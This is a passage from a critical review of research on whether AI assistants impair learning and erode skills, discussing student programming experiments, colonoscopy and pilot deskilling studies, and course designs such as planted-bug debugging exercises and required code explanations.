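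Some questions covered general programming concepts, and others covered details of the students' submitted solutions. Immediately after the task, 85% of students without AI could accurately recall a line of their own code, compared with 48% of those with ChatGPT. It isn't surprising that people forget code they didn't write, and a student who forgets a program may still know how to write a loop. The experiment is good evidence that the students with ChatGPT remembered less about their work, but weaker evidence that they became worse programmers, because nobody asked them to write a new program unaided.

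Time may explain part of the difference. Students with ChatGPT worked for 16 minutes on average and the others for 24, and three of those with ChatGPT finished the hardest problem in under a minute. Bergh and Vassar say they cannot separate the effect of spending less time from that of thinking less deeply. Fifteen students pasted the instructions or starter code into ChatGPT and accepted the answer, while 14 wrote the code themselves and used ChatGPT to check or debug it. One student asked it to act as a tutor and give only hints and questions, but the exchange became repetitive and the student ran out of time before finishing the second problem.

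### Answers and hints

*Generative AI Can Harm Learning*, by Bastani, Bastani and colleagues, reports an experiment with nearly a thousand pupils at a Turkish high school in the autumn of 2023. In each of four 90-minute mathematics sessions, a teacher reviewed a topic, the pupils worked through practice problems, and then they took an exam on similar problems without any help. The researchers randomly assigned whole classes to one of three conditions for the practice. Some classes had only their books and notes, some could also chat with a version of GPT-4 called GPT Base, and the rest could also chat with GPT Tutor, a version built with teachers' help. Both practice and exam counted towards pupils' grades.

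In one problem, pupils had to find the line through the point (−2, 3) parallel to 2x − 3y + 5 = 0. A pupil who asked GPT Base for the answer would typically get a full solution. The instructions for GPT Tutor included the correct answer and a list of common mistakes, and told the model not to give away the solution. If the pupil hadn't started, the model was to ask what they knew about the slopes of parallel lines.

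Adding the estimated effects to the average of the classes without AI gives these scores:

| Help during practice | Practice score | Exam score |
|---|---|---|
| Books and notes | 28% | 32% |
| GPT Base | 42% | 27% |
| GPT Tutor | 65% | 32% |

In relative terms, GPT Base raised practice scores by 48% and lowered exam scores by 17%. That 17% is a loss of about five percentage points, a smaller drop than Shen and Tamkin's even though the number is the same. GPT Tutor raised practice scores by 127% and made no measurable difference to exam scores.

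Two results suggest that many pupils simply copied GPT Base's answers. First, Bastani and colleagues found no clear sign that GPT Base had harmed learning by teaching wrong methods. It was right only 51% of the time when the researchers repeatedly asked it for the answers, but pupils' exam results were not clearly worse on problems that resembled the ones it reasoned about badly. Second, its arithmetic errors lowered practice scores about as much as its faulty reasoning did, although high-school pupils should be able to spot such errors. Copying would also explain why most conversations with GPT Base included a bare request for the solution.

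If copying is the problem, a more accurate assistant won't solve it. *AI Assistance Reduces Persistence and Hurts Independent Performance* (2026) reports experiments with GPT-5, a much stronger model. In one, 349 people practised fractions with the assistant and 318 without it, and then everyone worked on three more problems alone. Those who had used the assistant did worse and gave up more readily. Because this test began as soon as help was removed, it may partly measure frustration, so some of the loss could be motivation rather than missing skill. That explanation fits the Australian students' scores less well, because they were tested after two days.

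Unlike GPT Base, GPT Tutor had the correct answers and withheld them from pupils, and the experiment can't show which of these differences prevented the harm. Pupils with GPT Tutor did better during practice but learned no more than pupils with books and notes, although they believed they had done better in the exam. Pupils with GPT Base did not notice that they had learned less. The journal version of the paper has a narrower title, *Generative AI Without Guardrails Can Harm Learning*, which fits the evidence better.

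Other experiments with hints and feedback have found gains. In *ChatGPT-generated help produces learning gains equivalent to human tutor-authored help on mathematics* (2024), Pardos and Bhandari gave 274 people algebra and statistics problems with hints from ChatGPT, hints from human tutors or no help. Only the people with ChatGPT's hints learned significantly more than those without help, though the two kinds of hint did not differ significantly. *Toward Measuring AI's Effects on Skill Formation* (2026), a review of such evidence, describes a trial in which 968 people practised empathic communication while an AI assessed and guided them, and improved by almost a standard deviation. In that trial people did the task themselves and the AI commented, which is the opposite of having an assistant write the code. The review also cautions that researchers have randomly assigned software and kinds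 of feedback, but not how people think while using them. The idea that hints work by keeping people thinking is therefore still an inference, including for GPT Tutor.

### Studies that found no loss or a gain

Some studies of ordinary assistants have found no harm. In a 2023 experiment by Kazemitabaar and colleagues, novices learned Python with or without an AI code generator. According to Bergh and Vassar, the AI improved their coding but made no significant difference to what they retained, either immediately or a week later. Bergh and Vassar also cite a meta-analysis of AI tools in programming education, which found that students with AI worked faster and scored higher on tasks but had no significant advantage in learning. *Epistemic Transfer in AI-Assisted Verification* (2026) summarises a 2024 experiment by Karny and colleagues in which people did better while they had help but showed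 neither a loss of skill nor a lasting gain afterwards.

Such studies can miss a real effect, but their findings count equally against the views that learning with an assistant always leaves people worse off and that succeeding with one builds skill without further effort.

The strongest evidence of a gain comes from Contractor and Reyes (2026), in *Experimental Evidence on the Learning Impact of Generative AI*. They gave 211 students at Middlebury College in the United States up to 35 minutes to learn about blockchain, carbon capture or gene editing and write an essay. Students in some rooms could use ChatGPT, and about 70% of those students used AI. On a test without AI straight afterwards, students with access scored 7.2 percentage points higher than the others, and a week later they were 3.9 points ahead. Graders also gave higher ratings to the essays these students wrote without AI a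 week later. The immediate test had only five multiple-choice questions, so 7.2 points is about a third of a question per student.

Several differences between the experiments could explain why these students learned more with AI and Shen and Tamkin's programmers learned less. The Middlebury students spent the same amount of time learning whether or not they had AI, and those with AI spent more of it reading and searching and less of it writing. Their test performance also affected their pay, while the programmers received a flat fee and were told to hurry. The subject may also matter. Someone can learn how gene editing works by reading a good explanation, but finding a fault in a program also takes practice, and the Trio quiz emphasized questions that tested this skill.

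Middlebury students who asked AI to explain things kept their advantage a week later, while the lead of those who had it write the essay faded. Only 9% of the AI users, a handful of people, only had it write the essay, and the students all chose how to use it. The comparison therefore has the same limits as Shen and Tamkin's patterns, but the results are consistent with theirs.

What people already know may also determine whether they learn from an assistant. Contractor and Reyes cite a trial by Autor and colleagues in which an AI drafting tool improved the later unaided work of senior patent lawyers but not of junior ones. Perhaps only the senior lawyers knew enough to see why the AI's drafts were better than their own. If this holds for code, baseline knowledge would help people learn from an assistant as well as catch its mistakes, and those with the least knowledge would find it hardest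 to gain more. But Contractor and Reyes also cite a trial by Cruces and colleagues in which adults with less education kept some of their gains when they no longer had the AI, so the pattern is far from established.

### Months of use and agents

All these experiments are short. Shen and Tamkin's participants spent about an hour on Trio, a library that most of them had no need to learn. At work, the same people might use Trio every week, run into problems the assistant couldn't fix, and learn the concepts then, which would close the early gap. The gap could also widen, because each new concept builds on earlier ones and a person who skipped the basics may have to delegate more and more.

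Longer-term evidence is harder to interpret. *Faster Completion, Less Learning* (2026) analyses nearly three years of data from a commercial mathematics platform after the release of ChatGPT, and concludes that students spent less time on problems and learned less from them. It compares problems that students could easily hand to a chatbot with problems they could not, and supervised with unsupervised work. There was no random assignment, so other changes over those years could explain some of the difference. A meta-analysis of university studies, *Exploring the effect of GenAI on learning outcomes in higher education*, found no significant relation between the length of a course or experiment and the effect of AI. This gives no sign that harm builds up over time, but studies of different lengths also differ in many other ways.

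Agents leave the learner even less of the work than chat assistants do, and Shen and Tamkin expect them to impair learning more, because people using chat at least have to think about what to ask. *(Im)Paired Programming* (Balepur, Baumler and colleagues, 2026) provides some evidence for this. In the study, 54 computer science students built a variant of noughts and crosses for the web. Some used an agent that edited their files, and the others used a chatbot that gave only short, generic snippets, so they had to write or adapt the code themselves. The agent users' games met more of the requirements, but the agent users scored much lower than the chatbot users on 12 questions about their own code (d above 0.80).

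Everyone then had to extend the game without the agent, for instance by adding a reset button. The agent users did slightly better, apparently because they started from better code. When Balepur and colleagues compared students whose first versions were equally good, the agent users did worse. That comparison is less reliable than the randomized one, because a student who produced a good game with only the chatbot was probably a stronger programmer than one who did so with the agent.

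Students who had scored poorly on an earlier web programming test used the agent to make games as good as the stronger students' games, but understood them less well. The experiment had no group without AI, and it measured how well students understood one program rather than how much programming they had learned. It also lasted a couple of hours at most. A developer who works with an agent for a year will encounter failures that don't arise in such a short task, such as a design that has to be undone six months later, and may learn a good deal from fixing them.

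## Whether skills already learned fade with AI use

A developer who works with an agent for a year may also lose skills she already had. This deskilling is harder to demonstrate than a failure to learn, because someone must have measured her skills before she began using the agent.

### What would demonstrate deskilling

Imagine a firm that wants to know whether an agent has made its programmers worse at debugging. First, it has them find faults in unfamiliar programs without AI. They then use the agent for six months and take a second test, again without AI, on new programs of equal difficulty. The firm also tests similar programmers who spent those months without an agent, because scores can fall for other reasons, such as a harder second test or a tiring product launch. The effect of the agent is the difference between the two groups' changes:

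(AI users' second score − first score) − (other programmers' second score − first score)

If the AI users fall from 70% to 60% and the others from 70% to 66%, the agent accounts for six of the ten points the AI users lost. The firm should also choose at random who gets the agent, since the people who ask for it may already dislike debugging and practise it least.

Even then, a lower score could mean either that a programmer has forgotten how to trace a fault or that she still knows how but has grown used to waiting for the agent's suggestion. She could lose that habit after a few days of working alone, so testing her again after those days would help distinguish the two explanations.

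### The colonoscopy study

The best-known evidence that professionals lose skills by using AI comes from colonoscopy. In this examination, a doctor moves a camera through the large bowel to look for adenomas, growths that can become cancer. AI tools mark suspected growths on the video as the doctor watches. The usual measure of a doctor's performance is the adenoma detection rate, the share of examinations in which the doctor finds at least one adenoma.

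In *Endoscopist deskilling risk after exposure to artificial intelligence in colonoscopy*, Budzyń, Romańczyk and colleagues (2025) studied 19 doctors at four Polish centres that began using such a tool at the end of 2021. The doctors averaged 27.6 years' experience, and each had performed more than 2,000 colonoscopies. The tool switched on or off automatically depending on the date, so they still did many examinations without it. The researchers compared 795 examinations done without AI in the three months before the tool arrived with 648 done without it in the three months after. The detection rate fell from 28.4% to 22.4%, a drop of 6.0 percentage points (95% confidence interval 1.6 to 10.5). Adjusting for patients' age and sex made little difference.

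The study was observational, though it can be mistaken for a randomised trial because it took place inside one, which assigned patients to examinations with or without AI. Budzyń and colleagues took measurements before and after a period of AI use, but they had no comparison group because all their doctors had the tool in the second period.

A comparison group would have helped, because the number of examinations also rose between the two periods, from 795 to 1,382. Poland had suspended its colonoscopy screening programme on 1 January 2022, which let the centres take more patients from their waiting lists. Doctors with fuller schedules may have looked less carefully, but the researchers could not check this because they had no data on how long the doctors spent looking.

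The patients from the waiting lists may also have had fewer adenomas. In the second period, doctors using the tool found adenomas in 25.3% of examinations, compared with 28.4% without it in the earlier period. In a meta-analysis of 20 randomised trials, such tools raised the detection rate by about eight percentage points, so one would expect a higher rate with the tool unless there were fewer adenomas to find. The difference could be due to chance, though. Budzyń and colleagues instead suggest that unaided doctors in those trials had also got worse through exposure to AI, which would make the tools look more useful than they are.

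The fall was very uneven. Five female doctors did about a quarter of the examinations but accounted for more than 60% of the fall. Their rate fell from 37.5% to 22.4%, while the 14 men's rate fell from 25.2% to 22.4%, a change that could be due to chance. The centre with the highest starting rate, 39.7%, also had the largest drop. Budzyń and colleagues acknowledge that this could be regression to the mean, in which an unusually good period is followed by a more ordinary one because the first was partly due to chance.

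If the tool did cause the fall, lack of practice is an unlikely reason. In the second period, each doctor did an average of about 39 examinations with AI and 34 without it, compared with 42 before, not counting each centre's first 100 examinations after the tool arrived. The doctors had also been finding adenomas for decades, and Budzyń and colleagues argue that the skills of such experienced doctors would hardly change in three months. They use this argument to dismiss other influences over time, but it counts just as much against deskilling. They suspect that doctors who are used to AI become less motivated, focused and responsible when they work without it. That sounds more like a habit of waiting for the marks on the screen than a lost skill. A missed adenoma is just as bad for the patient either way, but a habit may be easier to reverse.

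#### Replies to the study

In a letter with the same title as the study, van de Sande, Sleijfer and colleagues (2025) suggest that doctors who can rely on a tool to spot growths may put more effort into other parts of the examination, such as exposing the whole bowel wall. They call this skill reallocation, and consider it unsafe only if hospitals fail to preserve the skills doctors need when the tool is missing or wrong. The Polish data can't show whether doctors reallocated their effort this way, because the researchers recorded what doctors found but not where they focused.

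*Faster AI, Uneven Frontier*, a July 2026 review by Margondai, Rader and colleagues, raises a different objection. Neither the number of adenomas per examination nor the number of advanced adenomas fell significantly, which the reviewers find hard to reconcile with a real loss of skill. This objection is fairly weak. Adenomas per examination did fall, from 0.54 to 0.43, and the drop narrowly missed significance (p = 0.071). Doctors found only about one advanced adenoma in every 16 examinations, so the study could easily have missed a decline in advanced adenomas.

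Replying to critics, including van de Sande and colleagues, Budzyń and two co-authors described their work as hypothesis-generating and called for trials to determine whether the effect is real.

### Later colonoscopy studies

Pedersen, Mori and colleagues (2026) reported in *Learning and deskilling effects of artificial intelligence in colonoscopy among endoscopists* that doctors' unaided detection of polyps, growths that include adenomas, did not stay low after they stopped using AI. Thirteen doctors at three Norwegian clinics did 5,013 colonoscopies between 2021 and 2025, first without AI, then with it, then without it again. The researchers counted the examinations in which a doctor found a polyp of at least 5 mm, which can be done without laboratory results.

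| Doctors | Before AI | With AI | After AI |
|---|---|---|---|
| 6 experienced | 28.3% | 26.7% | 27.2% |
| 7 less experienced | 31.9% | 39.5% | 36.3% |

Neither group's rate after AI differed significantly from its rate before. The less experienced doctors seem to have kept part of their gain, but this is mostly because the three who had found the fewest polyps did few examinations in the last phase. The remaining gain almost disappears when the analysis accounts for who did each examination.

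These results are reassuring but not conclusive. The confidence interval for the experienced doctors still includes a fall of about five percentage points, nearly as large as the one in Poland. The tool had not raised their detection rate, so they may never have relied on it much. The less experienced doctors were still learning, and their progress could have hidden a loss. There was again no comparison group of doctors who worked without AI throughout.

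The Polish and Norwegian results can both be right. The Polish doctors were still using AI on other days when the researchers measured their unaided work, while the Norwegian doctors had stopped. Pedersen and colleagues suggest that the effect may disappear once doctors no longer have the tool, which again fits a habit better than a lost skill.

Okumura, Kudo and colleagues (2025), in *Long-term impact of computer-aided adenoma detection*, followed doctors for three years at one Japanese centre that had AI in half of its examination rooms. Detection without AI did not decline. An editorial, *Long-term learning and not deskilling*, calls this robust evidence but notes that the team included developers of the AI system. It also says that the fall in the Polish study was greatest among less experienced doctors, although all the doctors in that study were experienced. Pedersen and colleagues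 note that doctors may improve over three years for reasons unrelated to AI, which could hide a loss of skill in the Japanese study too.

### What pilots keep and lose

Airline pilots have worked with automation for much longer. Casner, Geven and colleagues (2014), in *The Retention of Manual Flying Skills in the Automated Cockpit*, tested 16 pilots in a Boeing 747-400 simulator and varied how much automation they could use. With the autopilot off, pilots steered by hand but followed the computer's instructions. Without those instructions, they had to work out their course from the instruments. With everything off, they also had to keep track in their heads of where they were and where they should be going.

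The pilots still scanned their instruments and controlled the aircraft reasonably well. They had more serious trouble with thinking tasks, such as keeping track of their position without a map display, diagnosing failures and deciding what to do next. Casner told Inside Science that building and updating a mental picture of the flight is "flat-out intellectual work". The researchers suggest that how well pilots do this may depend on how actively they stay involved while the automation flies.

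The experiment tested the pilots in a single round, without measuring their skills years earlier or including a comparison group who had flown without automation. Some of the pilots may always have been poor at tracking their position. The experiment does show that a person can handle the controls well and still struggle to follow what the aircraft is doing, so testing one skill can't replace testing the other.

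Programming has a similar division. Writing a loop or remembering a command's options is a little like handling the controls. Working out which part of a program changes a customer's balance, and why the result is sometimes wrong, is more like tracking the aircraft. Reviewing code depends mostly on the second kind of skill. If programmers lose skills the way pilots do, a developer who tests herself by writing a short function without AI may conclude she has lost nothing, even though she can no longer follow data through ten files.

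The comparison with pilots is limited because steering an aircraft relies heavily on trained movements, while even writing a loop takes thought. Programmers may therefore have no skill that lasts as well as a pilot's handling of the controls. However, they can get practice by reviewing an agent's changes if they predict what each change will do before running it, instead of only waiting for the tests to pass. Making that prediction requires them to follow the program closely.

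### Programmers and security staff

Margondai and colleagues conclude that the evidence of deskilling in software engineering consists of self-reports and industry telemetry (data that software tools collect automatically), and that causal evidence is still pending. Their example of telemetry comes from GitClear, a company that analyses code changes. Farrag's *The Productivity-Reliability Paradox* (2026) describes an earlier GitClear analysis of 153 million changed lines, which projected that the amount of code developers undo or rewrite within two weeks would double by 2024. More rework could mean that developers have become worse at programming, that assistants write worse code, or that people try out more ideas. Because such data cover work done with AI, they don't measure what developers could do without it.

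Some papers cite findings about something else as evidence that skills have faded. Farrag writes that novice developers show "measurable skill atrophy" and cites two sources. The first is a 2024 paper that, he says, draws on aviation research to warn of skill decay. The second is a 2026 Anthropic publication, presumably Shen and Tamkin's experiment. Participants in that experiment learned a library they had never used, so they had no existing skill with it to lose.

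*Using Biometrics to Understand AI-Assisted Coding Performance and its Perception* (2026) cites the same experiment in its discussion of skill erosion, along with a study that recorded people's brain activity as they wrote essays. People who used a language model had weaker connectivity between brain regions while they wrote, but this doesn't show that they had become worse at writing alone. Margondai and colleagues consider the study suggestive at most, because it had only 54 participants and other researchers have published criticisms of its analysis.

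The same paper also discusses cognitive debt, the lack of understanding that builds up when a team produces code faster than its members can take it in. This can happen to a developer who has lost no skill. She could debug a program of similar size but has never properly read this one. Unlike a lost skill, this gap would not hold her back in a new job.

#### Studies that follow people over time

*The Impact of AI Coding Assistants on Software Engineering* (2026) surveyed 95 professional engineers who used AI assistants, then surveyed them again six months later. The engineers reported how they thought AI had affected their productivity, their experience of the work and the tasks they focused on, but they did not take a skills test. Their impressions are a poor substitute for one, given how badly the developers in the randomised trial described earlier misjudged their own speed.

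Hümmer, Durner and colleagues (2026), in *AI, Metacognition, and the Verification Bottleneck*, surveyed students and academic staff at a German institute of technology three times over about six months. The surveys had 21, 36 and 23 participants, as some people left and others joined. Most measures were self-reported, including how often people used AI, how they approached problems, and how sure they were that a solution was right and that they could prove it. The share who said they used AI every day rose from 52.4% to 95.7%.

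The objective measure was whether participants correctly solved four mathematical problems. The drop in accuracy that Hümmer and colleagues report, from 95.2% to 47.8%, is the difference between the easiest problem and the hardest, not a decline over six months. The two figures also seem to come from groups of different sizes, since 95.2% is 20 of 21 people and 47.8% is 11 of 23. The study had no control group, and participants could use ChatGPT on the problems, so their answers don't measure unassisted performance. The study documents growing use of AI among a few dozen people, but doesn't show whether they lost any skill.

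None of the studies that follow people over time, nor the pilot experiment, meets all four requirements for demonstrating deskilling:

| People | Skill measured before | Period of AI or automation use | Skill measured afterwards without it | Comparison group |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Polish doctors | yes | three months, on some days | yes | no |
| Norwegian doctors | yes | about 70 to 310 examinations each | yes | no |
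| Japanese doctors | yes | three years, in half the rooms | yes | no |
| Airline pilots | no | their flying careers | yes | no |
| German students and staff | no | about six months | no | no |
| Software engineers | no | at least six months | no | no |

Neither Thurner and colleagues nor Banstola and colleagues, whose security studies are described earlier, tested analysts without AI before and after a period of use. A SOC could do this by giving analysts the raw logs of some of its closed incidents with the assistant switched off, then repeating the test six months later with different incidents. If the SOC introduced the assistant to one shift at a time, the shifts still waiting for it would serve as the comparison group.

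Studies of earlier technologies don't clearly predict what such a test would find. Margondai and colleagues cite meta-analyses of 79 and 54 classroom studies in which pupils who used calculators got better at calculation and problem solving. They also cite a study in which people who habitually used satellite navigation had a steeper decline in spatial memory over three years. They hypothesize that generative AI may differ from both because it can take over the reasoning and writing as well as a single step.

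### When the person with AI does better

Even if researchers proved that AI erodes people's skills, people might still do better work with AI than they did before. On the Science Media Centre's website, an expert responding to the Polish study said one side of the argument is that lost skill doesn't matter if doctors identify more cancer.

Consider an analyst who used to judge 70% of difficult alerts correctly. She now judges 85% correctly with an assistant but would manage only 60% alone. If the assistant is unavailable for a share f of the alerts, her overall accuracy is:

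0.85 × (1 − f) + 0.60 × f

This stays above her old 70% until f reaches 0.6, so she would do worse overall than before only if the assistant were missing for more than 60% of alerts. But the average doesn't account for when the assistant is missing. An attacker who disables a network may also disable the assistant, just when a wrong judgement would do the most harm.

The argument also assumes that the person with AI does better, which isn't always true. In Poland, doctors with the tool found adenomas less often than they had without it a few months earlier. In the Japanese data, according to the letter *Artificial intelligence-supported polyp detection (CADe) at colonoscopy* (2026), doctors found invasive cancer more than twice as often without AI as with it. One explanation in the letter is that the tool distracts doctors with trivial growths. The study was observational, so the patients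 examined without AI may have had more cancer. Still, a tool that helps doctors find more growths could lead them to miss the important ones.

Mistakes that an assistant makes without any sign of trouble raise a harder problem than outages, because a person then has to notice that something is wrong. Let e be the share of an agent's changes that contain a serious fault, and c the share of those faults that the reviewer catches. The share of all changes that are faulty and still get through is:

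e × (1 − c)

In an example with invented figures, 10% of an agent's changes are faulty (e) and the reviewer catches 60% of the faults (c), so 40 faulty changes in every 1,000 get through. If her skill fades until she catches only 30%, the number rises to 70. But if the agent has meanwhile improved so that only 4% of its changes are faulty, she lets through 28 even with her faded skill, fewer than she did with the worse agent when she was skilled.

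Whether that is safer depends on the remaining faults. As agents stop making obvious mistakes, a larger share of the faults may be hard to see, like a missing authorization check, and 28 of those could do more harm than 40 ordinary bugs. Bainbridge's point about lost practice also applies, since the reviewer now meets a fault in only one change out of 25, and her catch rate may keep falling as the agent improves. For the other side of the argument, the expert at the Science Media Centre cited the danger that a biased AI, left unsupervised, could make its own mistakes on a massive scale. Many firms use the same few models, so a fault that one reviewer misses may also get past reviewers elsewhere. A colleague could still catch it, but if he has relied on the same assistant for just as long, he may have lost the same skill.

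## Programming courses that teach checking and unaided skill

A student in her first programming course has little skill to lose, but in a few years she may be a reviewer who has to catch an assistant's mistakes. Her teachers have to decide when to let her use an assistant. Some courses teach programming for several weeks before students use an AI model, some introduce one in the first week, and others offer an assistant that gives hints instead of answers.

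### Three orders of teaching

The University of Auckland's introductory C course for engineering students comes close to teaching the fundamentals first. Pădurean, Blake and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding Student Perceptions, Mistakes, and Debugging Approaches*, studied how more than 900 of the course's students worked with OpenAI's GPT-4o mini in 2024. The lab sessions with the model were in the seventh and ninth weeks, when students already knew some C. Each student saw a picture of a task, such as an array of numbers and the position of its last zero, and described the task in words to the model, which had no access to the picture.

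*Integrating Large Language Models and Evaluating Student Outcomes* (Vadaparty, Smith and colleagues, 2025) cites interviews in which some instructors wanted to ban AI from introductory courses because they feared students would stop learning the fundamentals. The Auckland researchers see a benefit in prompting, because students who don't have to produce correct syntax can concentrate on the problem. But they also warn that students who trust a tool are more likely to use its code without understanding it, which is an argument for waiting until students can read the model's code before introducing AI.

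After several weeks of studying C, the Auckland students still did not routinely read the model's code. When a prompt failed, they reported clarifying their wording or rereading the problem more often than tracing the code or looking at the test cases. This may be partly because the software let them change the prompt but not the code.

Vadaparty and colleagues took the opposite approach in a ten-week course at the University of California, San Diego, which introduced GitHub Copilot in the first week, together with functions, and reached variables and conditions in the second. They reasoned that employers expect people to use such tools, and that for people who generate code, splitting up problems, reading code and testing it matter more than writing it from scratch. They also wanted beginners to build larger projects on subjects they cared about. In lectures, the teachers showed wrong answers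 from Copilot and asked students to find the fault.

The final exam included seven questions about reading code that other researchers had already given to programming students in several countries. The San Diego students did about as well as the international average on six and 11% better on the seventh, which asked them to say in plain English what a loop was for. This suggests that early use of Copilot need not stop students from learning to read code, but these results don't show whether they write code as well as earlier classes did. San Diego's students may also be stronger than average, and their teachers encouraged them to do most homework problems without Copilot.

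In surveys halfway through and at the end of the course, about a quarter of the students said they relied on Copilot too much, and about one in seven said it got in the way of learning. One wrote, "I know people who can't code because of co-pilot". A few asked for it to be introduced later. Vadaparty and colleagues suggest that students felt this way because most exams excluded Copilot, and because 44% believed that professionals use such tools only rarely or sometimes. The students may also have been right that Copilot was hurting their learning. The exam averages don't show whether it was, because they don't compare heavy users of Copilot with light ones.

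Northeastern University tried a similar course with 11 students in the autumn of 2025. The course, described in *CS 1.5* (2026), combined programming with mathematics. For example, it taught recursion, in which a function calls itself, alongside proof by induction. Its teachers aimed to develop students' intuition, logic and professional judgement instead of their command of syntax. They call it a success, but a class of 11 without a comparison group can show only that such a course is possible.

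*Iris* (Bassner, Frankford and Krusche, 2024) describes a virtual tutor for programming exercises at the Technical University of Munich (TUM) that answers a student's question with a hint or another question, not a finished solution. According to TUM's *The Dissociation of Performance and Learning in AI-Supported Programming Education*, unrestricted AI may take away the struggle that students need for deeper learning, while a carefully built tutor can support them without replacing their own effort. A teacher can also leave the syllabus mostly unchanged and add lessons on what AI tools can and can't do, as *Teaching Introduction to Programming in the times of AI* (2025) proposes for another course.

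None of these courses randomly assigned students to different orders, and the courses differ in language, length and exams, so their results don't show which order works best.

### Planted bugs at Auckland

In 2025, the Auckland course changed its AI exercise so that a good prompt was no longer enough. Pădurean, Mahapatra and colleagues (2026), in *When AI Is Wrong on Purpose*, explain that models now solve beginners' problems so reliably that students have little reason to read the code. The new exercise works like this:

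1. The student describes the task in words, and GPT-4o mini writes a function in C.
2. The platform runs the function against hidden tests. If it fails, the student receives it unchanged.
3. If it passes, the same model, now with different instructions, writes five versions that are each meant to contain a small, realistic bug.
4. The platform runs these versions against the tests and gives the student the first one that compiles but fails.
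5. The student repairs the code or sends a new prompt. If the new prompt produces correct code, the platform plants another bug, so in most cases the student has to edit the code to finish.

In one task, students needed a function that finds the position of the last zero in an array. With a planted bug, it might look like this:

```c
int last_zero(int array[], int size) {
    for (int i = size - 1; i >= 0; i--)
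        if (array[i] == 0) return i + 1;
    return -1;
}
```

The function searches from the end of the array and should return the position of the first zero it finds. The planted bug is that it returns `i + 1` instead of `i`. For the numbers 4, 0, 7, 0, 5, the right answer is 3, because positions in C start at zero, but this function returns 4. A student who only glances at the code will see a sensible search in the right direction. To find the bug, she has to trace the value of `i` through one example.

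The exercise was a graded lab that students did at home within a week. Of the 1,037 students on the course, 917 took part, and Pădurean and colleagues analysed 2,636 sessions, each of which covers one student's work on one problem. They compared what students did when the first code they received had a planted bug with what they did when it was wrong because of the prompt or the model:

| First faulty code in a session | Ordinary fault | Planted bug |
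|---|---|---|
| Student edited the code first | 45% | 68% |
| Student sent a new prompt first | 52% | 31% |
| Next attempt succeeded | 51% | 90% |
| Next attempt succeeded, among those who edited | 63% | 92% |
| Typical size of the edit | 24 characters | 4 characters |

Students who received a planted bug were therefore more likely to edit the code directly and to succeed on their next attempt. The increase in editing was clear on the two easiest problems but not on two harder ones, and the fifth had too few planted bugs to tell.

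The higher success rate is largely a result of the design. The platform plants bugs only in code that already works, so the repair is small, while an ordinary fault may mean that the student has misunderstood or misdescribed the whole task. The figure for all attempts also counts a new prompt as a success if the model's next code would have passed before the platform planted another bug. A student whose first prompt was good could therefore send almost the same one again and succeed without reading anything. The 92% success rate among students who edited the code is more informative, because they got it to pass without going back to the model.

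Even that figure measures repair more than detection. The instructions warned students that the model was likely to make mistakes, and the platform showed them which test had failed, so they knew the code was wrong and had an input that proved it. Programmers in Kaufman and colleagues' experiment seldom looked for such a counterexample. About 93% of the code was faulty, so a student who always assumed there was a bug would rarely have been wrong. To measure detection, the course could hide the test results, leave some of the correct programs unchanged, and ask students which programs they would accept.

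Pădurean and colleagues did not test the students later without AI, and they had no comparison group that did the exercise without planted bugs. They propose adding both in future studies. Of the 917 students, 897 solved the two problems they needed for credit. However, they worked at home, so some may have asked another chatbot to find the bug.

Just over half of the students agreed that the bugs were easy to find and fix, and many said they had practised debugging and understanding code. One compared the exercise to chess puzzles, which train players to spot tactics in real games. The exercise restores the errors that an assistant normally removes, and Shen and Tamkin think people learn to debug through such errors. It is still unknown whether repairing several planted bugs makes students better at noticing a bug that no test has flagged.

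### Explaining code before using it

Another way to make students read generated code is to withhold it until they can explain it. Sankaranarayanan (2026), in *Mitigating "Epistemic Debt" in Generative AI-Scaffolded Novice Programming using Metacognitive Scripts*, tested this in an experiment that did include a task without AI. Epistemic debt is a developer's poor understanding of her own software, much the same as the cognitive debt described earlier. A metacognitive script is a set of prompts that leads learners through thinking steps they might otherwise skip.

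The 78 participants were mostly students, along with recent coding bootcamp graduates. They could write a loop and a function in JavaScript but had no professional experience with React, a library for building web pages. Sankaranarayanan randomly assigned them to three groups of 26 and gave them up to 90 minutes to build a website where students choose courses. One group had no AI. Another could freely use Claude 3.5 Sonnet in the editor Cursor. The third had the same assistant, but whenever participants wanted to apply its code, a window prompted them to explain why the code worked and how it handled "state updates" (changes to the data the page displays).

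A second model, GPT-4o, graded each explanation from 1 to 5 and released the code if the grade was 3 or higher. A participant who wrote that the code sends the course to the database and then changes the page would get a 2, because that only lists what the code does. To get a 3, the participant would have to explain that the program waits for the database to confirm the enrolment so that the page never shows a course the student isn't enrolled in. After a low grade, the model asked guiding questions and the participant tried again. Participants needed 2.4 attempts on average.

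Then everyone lost access to AI, and the researcher planted a bug in their websites. The enrolment code no longer waited for the database or undid a failed enrolment, so a course could appear on the page and vanish when the user reloaded it. Participants had 30 minutes to find the cause and fix it:

| Group | Website's average test score | Average building time | Fixed the bug without AI |
|---|---|---|---|
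| No AI | 65% | 88 min | 18 of 26 (69%) |
| Free use of AI | 92% | 48 min | 6 of 26 (23%) |
| AI with explanations | 89% | 65 min | 16 of 26 (62%) |

The groups with AI built equally good websites, but those who had to explain the code were much more likely to repair theirs. The 95% confidence interval for the difference in repair rates, calculated from the published counts, is about 14 to 63 percentage points. The effect could be modest or very large, but it is unlikely to be due to chance alone.

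A more serious problem is that participants had to explain in the window how the code handled state updates, and the planted bug was a faulty state update. Some had probably described the missing wait in their own words an hour before they met the bug. An extra bug in another part of the website, such as the check for overlapping courses, would have shown whether explaining code helps people understand the whole program or mainly the part they explained.

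The explanation group also spent about 16 minutes longer building, and Sankaranarayanan acknowledges that slowing people down might have helped by itself. The test followed immediately, so the experiment didn't measure how long the benefit lasts. Sankaranarayanan, who works for the company Extuitive, built the tool and is the paper's only author, but has published the software and materials so others can repeat the experiment.

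The paper also calculates each group's epistemic debt by subtracting its repair rate from its website score, which gives 69.3 points for the group that used AI freely and 27.6 for the group that gave explanations. The website score is an average and the repair rate is the share of people who fixed a single bug, so the difference between them has no clear meaning, and the repair rates alone are better evidence.

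In the free group, the six people who fixed the bug had asked the assistant an average of 4.2 questions about how its code worked, compared with 0.4 among the 20 who failed. As with Shen and Tamkin's six patterns, those who asked may have understood more to begin with. The comparison between groups is stronger evidence that making people explain code helps, because the explanation window was randomly assigned.

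Students may resent having to explain the code. In the explanation group, 72% at first called the requirement annoying or an obstacle. Most of the rejected explanations only restated the request or the names in the code. In a course, a student could also have another chatbot write the explanation. The method would then need supervision, or a teacher who asks the questions in person.

### Assistants that give hints

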